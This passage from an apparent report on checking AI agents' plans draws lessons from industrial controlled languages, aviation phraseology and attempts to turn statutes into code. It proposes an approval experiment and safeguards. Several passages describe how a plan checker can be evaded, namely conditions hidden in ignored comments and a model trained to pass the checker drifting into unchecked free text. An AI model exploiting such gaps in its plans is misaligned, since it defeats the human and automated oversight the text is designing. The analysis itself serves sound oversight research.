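Nobody has yet tested whether the people who would approve AI plans understand the plans they would see. An experiment should recruit purchasing managers or systems administrators and show them plans that agents wrote for realistic tasks. Each participant would read a short account of what the company wants, then approve or reject a series of plans. Some plans would have a hidden flaw, such as sending a second payment when a transfer times out. Most should be sound, as they would be at work, because people who rarely see a bad plan may stop looking for one.

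The researchers would assign participants at random to one of five versions:

| Version | What the participant sees |
|---|---|
| A | The plan in ordinary English |
| B | The plan in controlled English |
| C | The plan in controlled English, with a certificate from the checker |
| D | The same as C, plus three awkward cases that software has found |
| E | The plan in ordinary English, plus the same three cases |

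Comparing A with B would show whether the restricted language helps readers. Comparing B with C would show whether a certificate makes them less careful, and comparing D with C would show whether the cases make up for that. Version E would test whether the benefit comes entirely from the cases. If it does, ordinary English would serve readers just as well, and only the software would need the formal version.

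The main result should be the share of flawed plans that people approve, reported alongside the share of sound plans they reject, because a single accuracy score would hide the bias towards approval. The flaws should include some that the specification covers and some that it omits. Participants should also answer a few prediction questions, such as "could this plan pay the same invoice twice?", and say how sure they are.

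The researchers would need about 360 judgements of flawed plans for each version to distinguish reliably between readers who catch 60 per cent of flawed plans and readers who catch 70 per cent. In practice they would need more, because one person's judgements tend to resemble each other. If each participant judged ten flawed plans, 70 people per version would probably be enough.

If readers of version D caught clearly more flaws than readers of version A, including flaws outside the specification, the benefit to human approval would be an argument for requiring checkable plans. If readers of versions A and B caught about the same number, the argument for a restricted language would have to depend on what the checker catches. If people shown a certificate approved many more plans with flaws the specification omits than people shown none, a company would do better to let the checker reject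 plans silently and not show its managers a certificate.

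## What happened when industry and aviation adopted controlled languages

Experiments on readers last an hour or two, but an organisation that adopts a restricted language needs its staff to keep to it for years, under deadlines and with new things to describe. Manufacturers have tried to use such languages since the early 1970s, and pilots and air traffic controllers use one on every flight.

### Caterpillar's two languages

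By the early 1970s Caterpillar, the American maker of earthmoving machines, had more than 20,000 publications for mechanics who spoke over 50 languages. Translating everything would have produced more than a million documents. Verbeke's *Caterpillar Fundamental English* describes the cheaper plan the company introduced in July 1971, which was to write each manual once, in a simplified English that a trained mechanic could learn to read in 30 lessons. The vocabulary had about 800 words, only 70 of them verbs, and each word had one meaning. "Right", for example, was the opposite of "left" and never meant "correct".

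Verbeke, who managed service training at Caterpillar, gives an example of the improvement. The old wording required a lifting beam for all heavy objects "unless otherwise specified". The new wording, "Lift heavy objects with a lifting beam only", is easier to read but drops the exception. A mechanic with a special procedure would probably follow it anyway, but a checker would report a violation.

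Dealers were enthusiastic, and Verbeke expected other industries to copy the idea, but Caterpillar gave up the language in 1982. *Controlled Language for Multilingual Document Production*, by Kamprath, Adolphson and colleagues, gives the company's reasons. The vocabulary was too small to describe the electronics and high-pressure hydraulics that its machines had acquired. Up to a quarter of the mechanics in some developing countries left their jobs and took their training with them. Many customers also wanted manuals in their own language.

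Perhaps the most important reason was that nobody could enforce the rules. About 85 writers had received the vocabulary and guidelines, but only human editors could check the results, and very few manuals complied. Caterpillar still labelled the manuals compliant, and many mechanics who had taken the course couldn't read them. A company that merely told its AI agents to write plans in simplified English would run the same risk.

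In 1991 Caterpillar began work on a replacement, Caterpillar Technical English, which was meant to make translation cheap instead of unnecessary. Its vocabulary grew to about 70,000 terms. Hayes, Maxwell and Schmandt (1996), in *Controlled English Advantages for Translated and Original English Documents*, describe the checking program they helped to develop. It analyses each sentence with the same grammar as the translation program, so the translation program can parse any sentence that passes. If a sentence has two readings, the writer has to choose one. The heading "Clean Filters" could mean filters that are clean or an instruction to clean them.

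The developers had hoped to give every term a single meaning, but Kamprath and colleagues found more than 1,000 that needed several. "Charge", for example, can mean to charge a battery or to pressurise a gas cylinder. Writers of electrical manuals grew annoyed at having to rule out the gas cylinder meaning, so the developers let them declare their subject in advance. Even then, writers sometimes picked the wrong meaning, and some approved sentences were incorrect or incomprehensible.

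Missing words caused more trouble. New machines sometimes shipped before the names of their parts were in the dictionary, and Caterpillar let writers bypass the check when they needed a term the dictionary lacked. Writers were then tempted to skip the check for the whole passage. The company solved this by letting them request the new term and exempt only that term, so the program still checked the text around it. A plan language could do the same, provided that no action that depends on the missing word goes ahead until somebody has defined it.

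Hayes and colleagues admit that all this caused a "significant productivity hit" for the writers, which Caterpillar accepted because it expected to save more on translation. The company produced over 100,000 new pages a year, and all its writers worked in one building. At other companies, the writers were scattered and the savings would often have gone to a different department, so the writers had no reason to want the rules.

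### Ford's assembly instructions

Ford made a restricted language compulsory for its North American assembly instructions in 1990. According to Rychtyckyj's *Standard Language at Ford Motor Company* (2006), engineers write each instruction as a command built around one of 169 verbs, each of which stands for a single action. For example, "position" and "seat" are different actions. The word "using" always introduces a tool. A parser flags any sentence it can't analyse and tries to suggest a correction.

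The system works out the detailed steps from a valid set of instructions, and how long they will take. Kuhn adds that it can list the required parts. Assembly plants use the output to divide work among their staff, and planners can estimate the labour for a vehicle before anyone builds it. The engineers resisted at first, and some went to great lengths to document the system's errors, which helped the developers fix them sooner. By 2006 hundreds of engineers were using the language, and it had spread to plants in Europe, South America and Asia. Rychtyckyj, who worked on the system, calls it an overwhelming success, though he gives no count of errors before and after it was introduced.

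Engineers also got around the rules by putting comments in brackets, which the parser ignored. They often did this to avoid requesting a new term. One instruction in the paper is to secure a bumper bracket, with the comment "for LHS only", meaning the left-hand side. A worker will read that condition, but the program that calculates the steps and times will ignore it. If an agent's plan read "pay Acme [only if the goods arrive]", a checker that skipped comments would approve an unconditional payment.

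According to Kuhn, Boeing apparently never deployed Boeing Technical English, which extended the simplified English of aircraft manuals to other subjects. He gives no reason, but remarks that most controlled languages "die silently". Published histories therefore probably make success look more common than it is.

### Simplified Technical English

AeroSafety World's *Simplifying the Technicalities* (2007) repeats an anecdote from the UN's International Civil Aviation Organization about a technician who took "proscribed" in a bulletin to mean "prescribed" and carried out the forbidden procedure. The risk of such mistakes is considerable, since about 80 per cent of maintenance technicians are not native English speakers, according to *The case of English for aviation maintenance*.

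European airlines asked for a simpler English in the late 1970s, and international standards for aircraft maintenance documents have required one since 1987. The current version, Issue 9 of STEMG's *ASD-STE100 Simplified Technical English*, dates from January 2025. Maintworld's *The Role of Simplified Technical English in Aviation Maintenance* records that defence projects, including land and sea vehicles, also came to require the language. Boeing reports that companies in mining, oil exploration and software have adapted it or written their own.

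Its dictionary has about 1,000 general words. It allows "start" but not "begin", "commence" or "initiate". One rule bans strings of more than three nouns. Writers can add technical terms that fit one of 20 categories of names or 11 categories of verbs, so a company's full vocabulary may include thousands of words. This flexibility probably helps explain why the language has outlasted Caterpillar's fixed list, but it also makes compliance harder to judge. Boeing's checking program flags possible faults and lets the writer decide. Orlando Chiarello, chairman of the group that maintains the standard, told AeroSafety World that it was difficult to say how correctly manufacturers used it.

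In *To What Extent Does Text Simplification Entail a More Optimized Comprehension*, Jahchan, Condamines and Cannesson (2016) report criticism that the rules were based on anecdote and intuition. Most of the trials with readers came in the mid-1990s, years after the standards made the language compulsory. Shorter wording is not always clearer. In a 1976 NASA study, pilots reacted about a second faster to spoken sentences such as "The fuel pressure is low" than to two-word warnings such as "fuel low".

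Wang and Friginal (2025), in *From Tradition to Innovation?*, compared 8.2 million words of manuals from two generations of the same airliner. They report that the newer manuals use plainer language, but the paper's text and tables conflict on which generation scored higher for readability, so the direction of the change is uncertain. The study also can't be used to compare manuals from before and after the standard, because less than 4 per cent of the older generation's text dates from before 1990. The readability scores came from software, not from tests with technicians.

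One of their examples shows how such scores can mislead. A manual tells technicians to take a certain step if they expect a hard freeze *and* expect the tyres to freeze to the ground. The researchers split this into two sentences, one for the freeze and one for the tyres, each ending with the same instruction. The software rated the split version much simpler. But if h stands for the hard freeze, t for the frozen tyres and s for the step, the rule has changed from

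**(h ∧ t) → s** to **(h → s) ∧ (t → s)**

The original requires the step when both conditions are likely, but the simplified version requires it when either one is. For tyres, this means at worst some unnecessary work. If a company split "if the goods have arrived and the manager has approved, pay" in the same way, the agent would have to pay once the manager approved, even if the goods had not arrived.

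### Fixed phrases in air traffic control

The closest human parallel to an AI system stating its plan is a pilot telling an air traffic controller what the aircraft is going to do. The pilot must wait for permission before many manoeuvres.

The American version of the language has more than 300 fill-in-the-blank patterns. Kuhn's example is "United 623, in the event of missed approach, taxiing aircraft right of runway", which warns a crew about traffic beside the runway in case they have to abandon their landing. Other rules specify what a message should contain but leave the wording open. A warning about birds, for instance, should give their position, their species or size if known, their course and their altitude. When no pattern fits, controllers and pilots use ordinary English. This works only if both speak English well enough, and in 2004 ICAO moved to set a minimum standard for them.

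Kuhn puts this language in the same low precision class as Simplified Technical English, so a program couldn't interpret it reliably. Only seven of the hundred languages in his survey are meant for speech. He suggests that speech is harder to control because nobody can run a checker over a sentence before saying it.

Aviation instead checks a sentence after it is spoken. A pilot reads back the important parts of a clearance, such as the altitude, heading or runway, and the controller listens for mistakes. Kim Cardosi's studies of recordings from US control centres in the 1990s found errors in fewer than 1 per cent of these readbacks. At half a per cent, a centre with 10,000 readbacks a day would still have 50 errors for its controllers to catch.

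People also depart from the standard phrases quite often. In a survey the International Air Transport Association published in 2011, 44 per cent of airline pilots reported hearing non-standard phrases at least once per flight. Most of these departures do no harm, because the listener knows what to expect and understands anyway.

### Tenerife and Avianca Flight 52

On 27 March 1977 two Boeing 747s collided on a foggy runway in Tenerife, killing 583 people. The KLM aircraft was waiting at one end of the runway while the Pan Am aircraft was still taxiing along it. A departing crew needs both a route clearance and a separate clearance to take off. The KLM first officer told the tower that the aircraft was ready for take-off and waiting for its route clearance. The controller gave him the route clearance, which included the words "right turn after take-off".

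The first officer read back the route and added, "We are now at take-off." The controller thought this meant the aircraft was in position and waiting, but it was already moving. He replied "OK" and, after a pause, told the crew to stand by. At the same moment, the Pan Am crew radioed that they were still on the runway, and the overlap made both transmissions harder to hear in the KLM cockpit.

Spain's official report found that the fundamental cause was that the KLM captain took off without clearance. It listed inadequate language as a contributing factor and recommended keeping "take-off" out of route clearances. Controllers now say "take-off" only to give or cancel permission for it, and otherwise say "departure".

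The readback did not help, because it tested only whether the crew had received the route. The danger came from a phrase that the first officer improvised and added to the end of a valid message. In the terms used for AI plans, the crew's statement was a report and not a gate, because no equipment held the aircraft in place until the tower cleared it.

Avianca Flight 52 ran out of fuel near New York's Kennedy airport on 25 January 1990, after controllers had kept it circling for over an hour. Of the 158 people on board, 73 died. The crew had asked for "priority" and said they would run out of fuel, but they never declared an emergency. After a failed attempt to land, the captain told the first officer to say they had an emergency. The first officer told the controller they were running out of fuel, then assured the captain he had passed the message on.

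The US National Transportation Safety Board blamed the crew for managing their fuel badly and failing to communicate the emergency. It also cited the lack of standardised, understandable terms for low fuel. ICAO later introduced the calls "minimum fuel" and "Mayday fuel".

"Emergency" would have obliged the controllers to put the flight ahead of others, whereas "running out of fuel" left them to judge how serious the problem was. Standard words work partly because listeners know exactly what to do when they hear them, but listeners may then give too little weight to a warning in other words. An agent's warning could fail in the same way if the agent wrote "the supplier's new account looks slightly unusual" in a comment instead of using the plan language's term for referring a payment to a manager.

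### Typed messages

Over oceans, and increasingly elsewhere, controllers and pilots exchange typed messages by data link. Most are standard elements with blanks to fill in, such as "climb to" followed by a level. Some aircraft can load certain standard messages, such as a new route, directly into the flight computer, but not free text. ICAO therefore advises using free text only when no standard element will do.

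Fixed wording can still be misread. A message may tell a crew to climb *at* a certain time or place, and some crews have overlooked the "at" and climbed immediately. The recommended remedy is to begin the message with an instruction to maintain the present level. This instruction is logically redundant, but it makes the condition much harder to miss. A plan language could likewise show approvers "do not pay yet" before "pay when the goods arrive".

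### Why some of the languages lasted

The languages that lasted all deal with a narrow subject in which the same situations keep coming up. They differ more in other respects:

| Language | How mistakes come to light | What people do when a word is missing | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| Caterpillar Fundamental English | Human editors | No general solution | Dropped in 1982 |
| Caterpillar Technical English | Checking program | Request the term and exempt it | In regular use by the mid-1990s |
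| Ford's Standard Language | Parser | Request the term, or write a comment | In use worldwide by 2006 |
| Simplified Technical English | Editors and optional programs | Add an approved kind of technical term | Still required |
| Air traffic phraseology | Readback | Use plain English | In use worldwide |

Automatic checking mattered at Caterpillar and Ford because another program had to process the text, as a plan checker would. It was not essential where only people had to understand the result. A controlled language also seems more likely to last if it benefits the people who have to write or speak it, as when a pilot who speaks clearly is immediately safer. But Caterpillar's language mostly burdened its writers, and it lasted because a central management wanted it. These cases can suggest what to look for but can't prove which feature made the difference, because there are only five and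 most of the evidence on the company languages comes from people who built or managed them.

### What changes when the writer is an AI system

AI systems would remove several of the obstacles. They don't leave after a year and take their training with them, and they can rewrite a rejected sentence in seconds without resenting it. Thousands of agents at many companies could also share one plan language, which would spread the cost that made Caterpillar's system so hard to copy. Caterpillar alone needed about five full-time staff a year from 1992 to 1997, although AI could now do much of the work on the vocabulary.

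AI systems would not necessarily keep to the spirit of the rules. Ford's engineers used comments to save themselves trouble. Training a model to pass a checker would push it towards free text more strongly, because nothing written there can cause a rejection. This is an inference from how training works, and none of the adoption histories tests it. A sensible precaution is to let free text explain an action but never authorise it or set conditions on it. A company could also track how much of its agents' plans is free text, and treat a recurring comment as a sign that the language needs a new term.

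Better discipline wouldn't stop an agent from choosing the wrong sense of "charge", as a technical writer might, and the checker would still accept the sentence. The agent could also fail to recognise an emergency. When software can measure the relevant conditions, the system shouldn't rely on the agent to declare one. If a supplier's account number doesn't match the register, the payment program can refer the matter to a manager itself, whether or not the agent's plan mentions it.

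## What happened when statutes were turned into code

Industrial controlled languages cover narrow subjects, and people writing in them can reword an instruction that the language doesn't allow. Someone formalising a statute can't reword it, and legislators intend it to govern cases they didn't foresee. Computer scientists and lawyers have been trying to turn statutes into logic for more than forty years. Their attempts are the best evidence on whether rules keep their meaning and purpose when formalised.

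### The British Nationality Act in Prolog

In the summer of 1983 Fariba Sadri, a student at Imperial College London, translated about 50 of the 73 pages of the British Nationality Act 1981 into logic. It took her two months, without help from a lawyer. *The British Nationality Act as a Logic Program* (Sergot, Sadri and colleagues, 1986) describes the result, an estimated 500 rules in the programming language Prolog.

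The Act's first clause covers people born in the United Kingdom after the Act came into force. They are citizens if, at the time of birth, either parent is a citizen or is settled in the country. In condensed form, the translation is:

```
citizen(X)       if  born_in_uk(X, D) and in_force(D)
                     and qualifies(X, D)
qualifies(X, D)  if  parent(Z, X) and citizen(Z, D)
qualifies(X, D)  if  parent(Z, X) and settled(Z, D)
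```

The capital letters are blanks for a person, a parent and a date. The rules are Horn clauses, the form of logic that Meijer's car dealer uses for its business rules. The program works backwards from the conclusion that Peter is a citizen. It checks where and when he was born, then who his father is, and then whether the father was a citizen on that date. It can also list the rules it used.

Later sections of the Act repeatedly forced changes to rules already written. Section 47 makes some children legitimate when their parents marry after the birth, and a man counts as the father only of his legitimate children. Because a man could therefore legally become a child's father after the birth, "Z is a parent of X" had to become "Z is a parent of X on date D", and every rule that mentioned parents had to change. Sergot and colleagues write that it was largely a matter of luck whether a change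 was easy. They saw no alternative to trial and error, because nobody can prove that a set of rules matches an English text.

### When nobody knows the facts

Negation caused the most trouble. Under section 1(2), a newborn baby found abandoned in the United Kingdom counts as the child of a qualifying parent "unless the contrary is shown". Let P be "this child has a qualifying parent". Prolog and the Act then fill a gap in the evidence in opposite ways:

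- **Prolog:** if nobody can prove P, conclude "not P".
- **The Act:** if nobody can prove "not P", conclude P.

When both parents are unknown, nobody can prove that either one qualifies. The Act still makes the baby a citizen, but a direct translation that relied on Prolog's convention of treating whatever can't be proved as false would not. Sergot and colleagues avoided this by having the program ask the user about the parents' status only after someone had identified both of them. They also found a gap in the Act: if the parents turn up later and neither qualifies, the reason for treating the child as a citizen disappears, but the Act has no provision for that.

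A purchasing agent's plan can go wrong in the same way. PDDL, like Prolog, normally treats anything the description leaves out as false. The precondition `(not (damaged ?order))` is therefore true of a crate that nobody has opened. The payment action in the earlier example avoids this error only because it also requires an inspection.

Prolog's convention works better for ordinary exceptions. Section 11 of the Act gives citizenship to a large group of people and then excludes some of them. The translation adds the condition "and not excluded by section 11(2)", which holds unless the program can show that the exclusion applies.

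Prohibitions need different treatment from ordinary rules. Kowalski's 1989 paper *The Treatment of Negation in Logic Programs for Representing Legislation* discusses a clause that forbids a minister to take away someone's citizenship unless satisfied that this serves the public good. Written as an ordinary rule, the clause would be: "the minister is satisfied if the minister takes away citizenship". Given the fact that the minister has taken away someone's citizenship, a program using this rule infers that the minister was satisfied, so the rule can never catch a violation.

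Kowalski instead treats the clause as a constraint:

**not (A and not C)**

He then adds C as a condition to every rule that allows the minister to act. A company faces the same choice with the rule "never pay without the manager's approval". If an engineer enters the rule as a fact about how payments work, a checker will infer from any payment that the manager approved it. The engineer has to enter the rule as a test that the plan can fail.

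### Good character and vehicles in the park

The Act also uses phrases such as "good character" and "sufficient knowledge of English" without defining them. Sergot and colleagues left these as conditions for someone else to settle, so that the program could give a qualified answer such as "Peter is a citizen, if he is of good character." They treated ministerial discretion similarly. Where a minister may extend a time limit from twelve months to six years, one rule applies the normal limit, and another applies the longer limit only if the minister decides to extend it.

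This keeps the judgement visible, but somebody still has to make it. *The British Nationality Act as a logic program (Sergot et al. 1986)*, an assessment by the computational law research project COHUBICOL, objects that the program lets its user supply the answer, when only courts and tribunals can settle what such terms mean. An applicant who told the program they were of good character would get a definite result with no legal standing.

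Philip Leith made a deeper objection in his 1986 article "Fundamental Errors in Legal Logic Programming". He denied that a statute contains clear rules for a programmer to copy out, because a legal rule gets its meaning from what lawyers and courts do with it. On this view, translating the vague phrases carefully doesn't help, because the apparently clear ones are also open to interpretation.

Sergot and colleagues had already conceded part of Leith's criticism. They wrote that they were trying only to apply rules mechanically to individual cases, not to simulate legal reasoning, and they had chosen the Act partly because it was too new to have any case law. They also reported less ambiguity than they had expected and said the intended reading was usually easy to identify. That doesn't fully answer Leith, because computer scientists decided which reading was intended.

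The legal philosopher H. L. A. Hart had taken a position between these two. He used "open texture" to mean that a word can have settled uses and still leave new cases undecided. His example was a rule that bans vehicles from a park. It plainly covers a car, but nobody can tell from the word "vehicle" alone whether it covers roller skates or a toy car. Open texture affects precise words as well as vague ones like "reasonable", because cases can arise that nobody had imagined. "Mother" looked like one of the Act's easy terms, but once a woman could give birth to a child from another woman's egg, it had two possible meanings. Parliament had to choose between them in a 1990 statute.

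Hart's critic Lon Fuller pointed out in 1958 that a rule can produce a bad result even when its words are clear. Suppose some veterans want to put a working army truck on a pedestal in the park as a war memorial. The truck is certainly a vehicle, but there is no obvious reason to exclude it under a ban meant to keep the park quiet and safe. The supplier formula has the same problem when it requires payment for wrong but undamaged goods.

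Leith's objection is therefore too strong for the many cases in which nobody disputes where someone was born or whether a crate is crushed. But it gives good reason to doubt that anyone can list all the disputed cases in advance.

### Several coders, one Copyright Act

If a statute's meaning were plain from its text, trained people coding it separately should produce similar code. An Australian experiment tested this in late 2020. Three legally trained research assistants who had coded legislation together before translated parts of Australia's Copyright Act 1968 into defeasible deontic logic, a formal language for obligations and permissions in which one rule can override another.

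In the first week, each of the three coders worked alone on the exceptions for "fair dealing", such as copying for research. Before the second week, they spent two hours agreeing on key terms, then each worked alone on the sections that define copyright and infringement. The researchers measured similarity by dividing the number of terms or rules that two coders shared by the average number each had written. If one coder wrote 20 terms, another wrote 30 and they had 5 in common, the similarity would be 5/25, or 20 per cent.

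*An Empirical Evaluation of a Coding Legislation Methodology* (2025) reports a follow-up with two groups of four law students in Dhaka. The students learned a fixed procedure for building terms from a sentence's subject, verb and object. They coded some sections under the researchers' supervision, then others without it. The table shows the similarity in both experiments, first for the code as written and then after the researchers had dealt with superficial differences. In the 2020 experiment, this meant tidying names, tenses and faulty structure. In the follow-up, it meant matching terms and rules that had the same meaning.

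| Condition | Terms as written | Rules as written | Terms after matching | Rules after matching |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2020, no agreed terms | 4% | 0% | 40% | 17% |
| 2020, agreed terms | 58% | 1% | 85% | 39% |
| Follow-up, supervised | 89% | 87% | over 97% | over 97% |
| Follow-up, unsupervised | 47% | 18% | 58% | 38% |

The zero is less alarming than it looks, because two versions can have no rules in common by this measure and still always give the same result. For example, one coder might write "if A or B, then C" as a single rule, and another might write "if A, then C" and "if B, then C" as two. For one provision on commercial rental, one of the 2020 coders used a single rule and another used three, and both versions were valid.

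Other differences affected the meaning. One coder combined "research or study" into a single term, while another kept them separate, as an Australian court had done. The Act also lists matters that a person "shall" consider when deciding whether a use is fair. One coder recorded these as facts instead of duties, so a checker using that version couldn't detect when someone had failed to consider them.

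Agreeing on vocabulary clearly helped people choose the same terms, but it did much less to make them write the same rules. The follow-up's higher scores are encouraging, but its supervised students worked under very different conditions from the unsupervised coders of 2020. When the students worked without supervision, the similarity of their rules fell from 87 to 18 per cent, though they were also coding different sections. Some had confused a provision's conditions with its consequences. Both experiments were tiny, and neither measured whether the rules were correct, which matters because two groups with the same training can make the same mistake.

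A better test would run each version on the same concrete cases and count how often the outcomes differ. For a company's agents, different wording wouldn't matter, but allowing a payment in one version and blocking it in another would matter a great deal. The coders' professional backgrounds may also affect the outcome. Burdon (2024) distinguishes computational, legal and regulatory ways of reading a legal text, which lead to different choices in the code.

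### Fifteen teams and a bankruptcy law

Escher, Bilik and colleagues (2024), in *Code-ifying the Law*, asked fifteen teams to turn part of the US Bankruptcy Code into a program that advises the public, then checked whether the programs were correct. Nine teams consisted of one or two computer scientists, and six paired a computer scientist with a law student.

The provision lists debts that survive bankruptcy, including debts for fraud, debts for child support and similar payments, and some student debts unless repaying them would cause "undue hardship". Courts treat each debt separately, so a person who owes both child support and student debt needs advice on both. Lawyers don't dispute this part of the law, and scholars often recommend such clear rules as the safest to automate.

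Only two of the fifteen programs got it right, one from each kind of team. Some programs stopped asking questions as soon as the user mentioned child support. Several teams of computer scientists thought people who owed money for fraud could escape the debt by taking out a student loan. One pair said this seemed wrong but took it to be what the text meant. Escher and colleagues found these errors by trying the programs on imaginary users with several kinds of debt, a test the teams could have run themselves.

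Six of the nine teams of computer scientists asked users whether "undue hardship" applied to them. Two others borrowed a definition from disability law, and one left the exception out. The law students knew that courts disagree about the phrase, but five of the six mixed teams made the rule stricter than the courts do. Many replaced the courts' "minimal" standard of living with the federal poverty line because they believed a computer needed sharp categories, although judges have cancelled the loans of people above that line.

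A strict rule can be sensible for a payment gate, because a company loses little by delaying an honest invoice. In bankruptcy, however, a strict rule means people are told they can't escape a debt that a court might cancel. Whoever formalises a vague standard should therefore consider who would be harmed by making it stricter.

The computer scientists were confident in their work. Sixteen of the 19 would have let their program advise the public, and 15 would have let court clerks use it to decide cases. Four of the six law students accepted the first use, and none accepted the second. The participants were students or recent graduates with at most five hours for the task, so the error rate is weak evidence about well-funded professional teams. But the experiment shows that adding a lawyer isn't enough. In half of the mixed teams, the law student took no part in testing. In the mixed team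 that succeeded, the partners kept explaining the law and the code to each other.

### Catala and French family benefits

Catala is a programming language for tax and benefit law, designed for lawyers and programmers to collaborate. Merigoux, Chataing and Protzenko (2021) describe how a lawyer and a programmer work through a statute together. They place each paragraph of the law beside the code that implements it, so the lawyer can review the code without writing any.

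Statutes usually state a general rule and list the exceptions later, and Catala keeps that order. Under section 121 of the US tax code, people who sell their main home can exclude up to $250,000 of the gain from their taxable income. Paragraph (2)(A) raises the limit to $500,000 for certain married couples. In simplified form, the code is:

```
definition gain_cap equals $250,000

exception definition gain_cap
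  under condition paragraph_A_applies
  consequence equals $500,000
```

If paragraph (2)(A) applies, the exception replaces the general rule. Catala writes the general pattern as

**⟨e₁, …, eₙ | c :- v⟩**

Here the e's are exceptions, c is the condition for the general rule, and v is its result. If exactly one exception applies, the program uses it. If none applies and c is true, the result is v. If two exceptions apply, the program stops and reports a conflict.

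Suppose a company pays suppliers after 30 days, pays small suppliers after 10, and holds payment on disputed orders. If a small supplier's order is in dispute, both exceptions apply. A program that checked them in a fixed order would apply whichever came first without flagging the conflict. With Catala, somebody has to decide which exception takes priority.

Writing a statute in Catala also exposes assumptions. Section 121 requires the seller to have owned the home for two years, but Catala has no built-in length for a year. The programmer had to find the regulation that defines a year as 365 days for this purpose.

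Merigoux and colleagues used Catala to write the rules for French family benefits, which come from 27 articles of the Social Security Code and several executive orders. The code and the text of the law came to about 1,500 lines. They compared the results with the government's online calculator and found no errors in the cases the calculator covered, which excluded children in the care of social services. They then read the calculator's published source code, part of the OpenFisca project, and found that it applied an income limit to families with one child in France's overseas territories, who are exempt from that limit. The OpenFisca developers corrected the mistake.

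This is good evidence that careful formalisation can make a rule more faithful to the law than ordinary programming does. But Merigoux and colleagues chose statutes well suited to formalisation. They describe these statutes as algorithms in disguise, and they exclude areas where officials have to use judgement. The work is also slow. Four two-hour sessions with tax lawyers covered about 15 per cent of section 121.

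Reviewers can still miss errors in the code. Merigoux and colleagues showed 18 law students with no programming experience part of the section 121 program, in which one comparison had been reversed from "at least" to "at most" or vice versa. After a short question session, seven students were willing to certify that the code matched the law, and only two of those seven spotted the mistake. Merigoux and colleagues find this encouraging after a two-hour introduction, but it is a warning for a company that relies on such reviews to approve its rules. The result also fits the experiments on temporal logic.

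### Which text has authority

In 2020 the OECD, whose members are mostly wealthy democracies, proposed in *Cracking the code* that governments issue an official version of their rules for computers to use. In July 2026 it opened a consultation on "law as code", which proposes that governments publish machine-executable versions of their laws for public bodies, courts, businesses and AI systems to share. The written law would remain the binding source, so it would prevail if the code disagreed with it, and each piece of code would link to the text behind it. The code would still show which matters call for interpretation or discretion, much as the Nationality Act program did with "good character".

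The OECD is too optimistic when it adds that this would eliminate the gap between legal text and its application. One official translation would spare hundreds of agencies from making their own, and correcting it once could correct it everywhere. But its writers would face the same choices as the Australian coders, and every system that used it would share their mistakes until someone noticed.

For AI plans, the OECD's approach would mean that the company's English instruction prevails over its formal specification. An agent that paid for the wrong goods could not then defend itself by pointing to the formula. (A US proposal for securities went further and would have made issuers file a working program alongside the prose.)

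A statute can prevail over the code that implements it because a court can interpret the statute afterwards. Australia's Robodebt scheme, an automated system for recovering welfare payments, demanded repayment of hundreds of thousands of debts that people did not owe. A class action led to a settlement worth more than A$1.8 billion. The remedy came late and could not undo all the harm, but the courts could still apply the law instead of the program's version of it.

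A plan checker, by contrast, approves or blocks a plan before the agent acts. If it blocks a good plan, the agent or its user can appeal to a manager, who can read the English instruction and let the plan through. But if the checker approves a payment that the instruction forbade, a later ruling won't bring the money back. For irreversible actions, the formal specification therefore determines what the agent can do, whatever the company has declared about its English version.

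The checker could instead give a qualified answer, as the Nationality Act program did. If it answered "This plan passes, if the goods are the ones we ordered", the manager would know to check the goods before the payment goes out. This works for judgements the specification's author has marked, but not for a case like Fuller's truck, where the rule seems clear and nobody thinks to ask whether it applies.

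In other ways a company has an easier task than a legislature. It can ask the manager what an instruction was for, whereas hundreds of legislators may have voted for a clause for different reasons, or kept it vague because they couldn't agree. It can also change its specification the same day. But a manager's decision about one plan doesn't affect the next unless someone adds it to the specification, while a higher court's interpretation binds lower courts in later cases.

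## The US proposal to make securities issuers file payment rules as code

The OECD's consultation asks governments to publish their own rules as code. In April 2010 the Securities and Exchange Commission (SEC), which regulates US investment markets, proposed a similar duty for private companies. Most companies that sold asset-backed securities to the public would have had to file a working computer program that implemented the rules for paying investors. The proposed requirement never took effect, but it is a close precedent for requiring an AI system to state its commitments in a formal language.

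An asset-backed security gives its holder a share of the payments from a pool of loans, such as mortgages or car loans. The securities usually come in several classes. Investors call the rules for dividing each month's cash among the classes a waterfall, because in the simplest version cash reaches a lower class only after the class above it has received its full amount.

### One month's cash

Suppose a pool of car loans backs two classes. This month Class A is due $700,000 and Class B is due $300,000. The contract might read:

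> On each payment date, the trustee shall use the cash collected to pay first the amount due to Class A and then the amount due to Class B.

The same rule in Python, a widely used programming language, is:

```
def waterfall(cash, due_a, due_b):
    paid_a = min(cash, due_a)
    paid_b = min(cash - paid_a, due_b)
    return paid_a, paid_b
```

The function `min` returns the smaller of two numbers. If borrowers pay $1 million, both classes receive everything they are due. If some borrowers miss payments and only $800,000 arrives, Class A still gets $700,000 and Class B gets the remaining $100,000. A contract that shared the cash in proportion to what each class was due would have given Class A $560,000 and Class B $240,000.

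Neither the English nor the code specifies whether Class B's investors will get the missing $200,000 next month or have lost it for good, so another clause would have to cover that. Real waterfalls have many such clauses. Some send cash to a reserve fund, and others switch from proportional payment to strict order when losses rise.

### What issuers would have had to file

Large investors usually value these securities by simulating many possible futures, with different interest rates, defaults and early repayments, and running each one through the waterfall. They need the waterfall as a program to do this, but issuers only had to publish an English description.

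The SEC (2010) observed that the issuer or its bank generally had a computer model but did not have to share it. Investors had to translate the English payment rules into code themselves or buy a translation. They often could not finish in time to decide whether to invest, and some would make mistakes. The SEC also thought the difficulty encouraged investors to rely too heavily on credit rating agencies, whose ratings of mortgage securities had failed badly in the financial crisis.

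Under the proposal, an issuer would file Python source code on the SEC's public database. An investor would download it, load a file of loan data, and enter assumptions about factors such as defaults and interest rates. The program would then calculate the payments to every class until the securities matured. The program would be part of the prospectus, the legal document that describes the securities to investors. A material change to it would require a new filing and another five-business-day wait.

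The issuer would also supply sample inputs with the expected results, so investors could confirm that the program ran properly. This test would not catch a mistranslation of the contract. If the issuer's programmer had misread the clause on shortfalls, the expected results would contain the same mistake, and the investor's results would match them. The SEC did not plan to test the code before issuers filed it.

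### What it would have cost

The SEC assumed that issuers already had their waterfalls in some programming language and would only have to convert them. It estimated that each sponsor, the company that organises the deals, would spend 672 hours setting up the conversion and then two hours on each deal checking that it had worked. The table compares the SEC's yearly estimates for the program with its estimates for the loan data in the same package of proposals.

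| | Waterfall program | Loan data |
|---|---|---|
| Filings | 958 | 16,534 |
| Hours of issuers' own staff time | 10,055 | 193,099 |
| Outside costs | $7.8 million | $41.3 million |

On these figures the program was much the cheaper requirement, yet the SEC eventually adopted the loan data and not the program.

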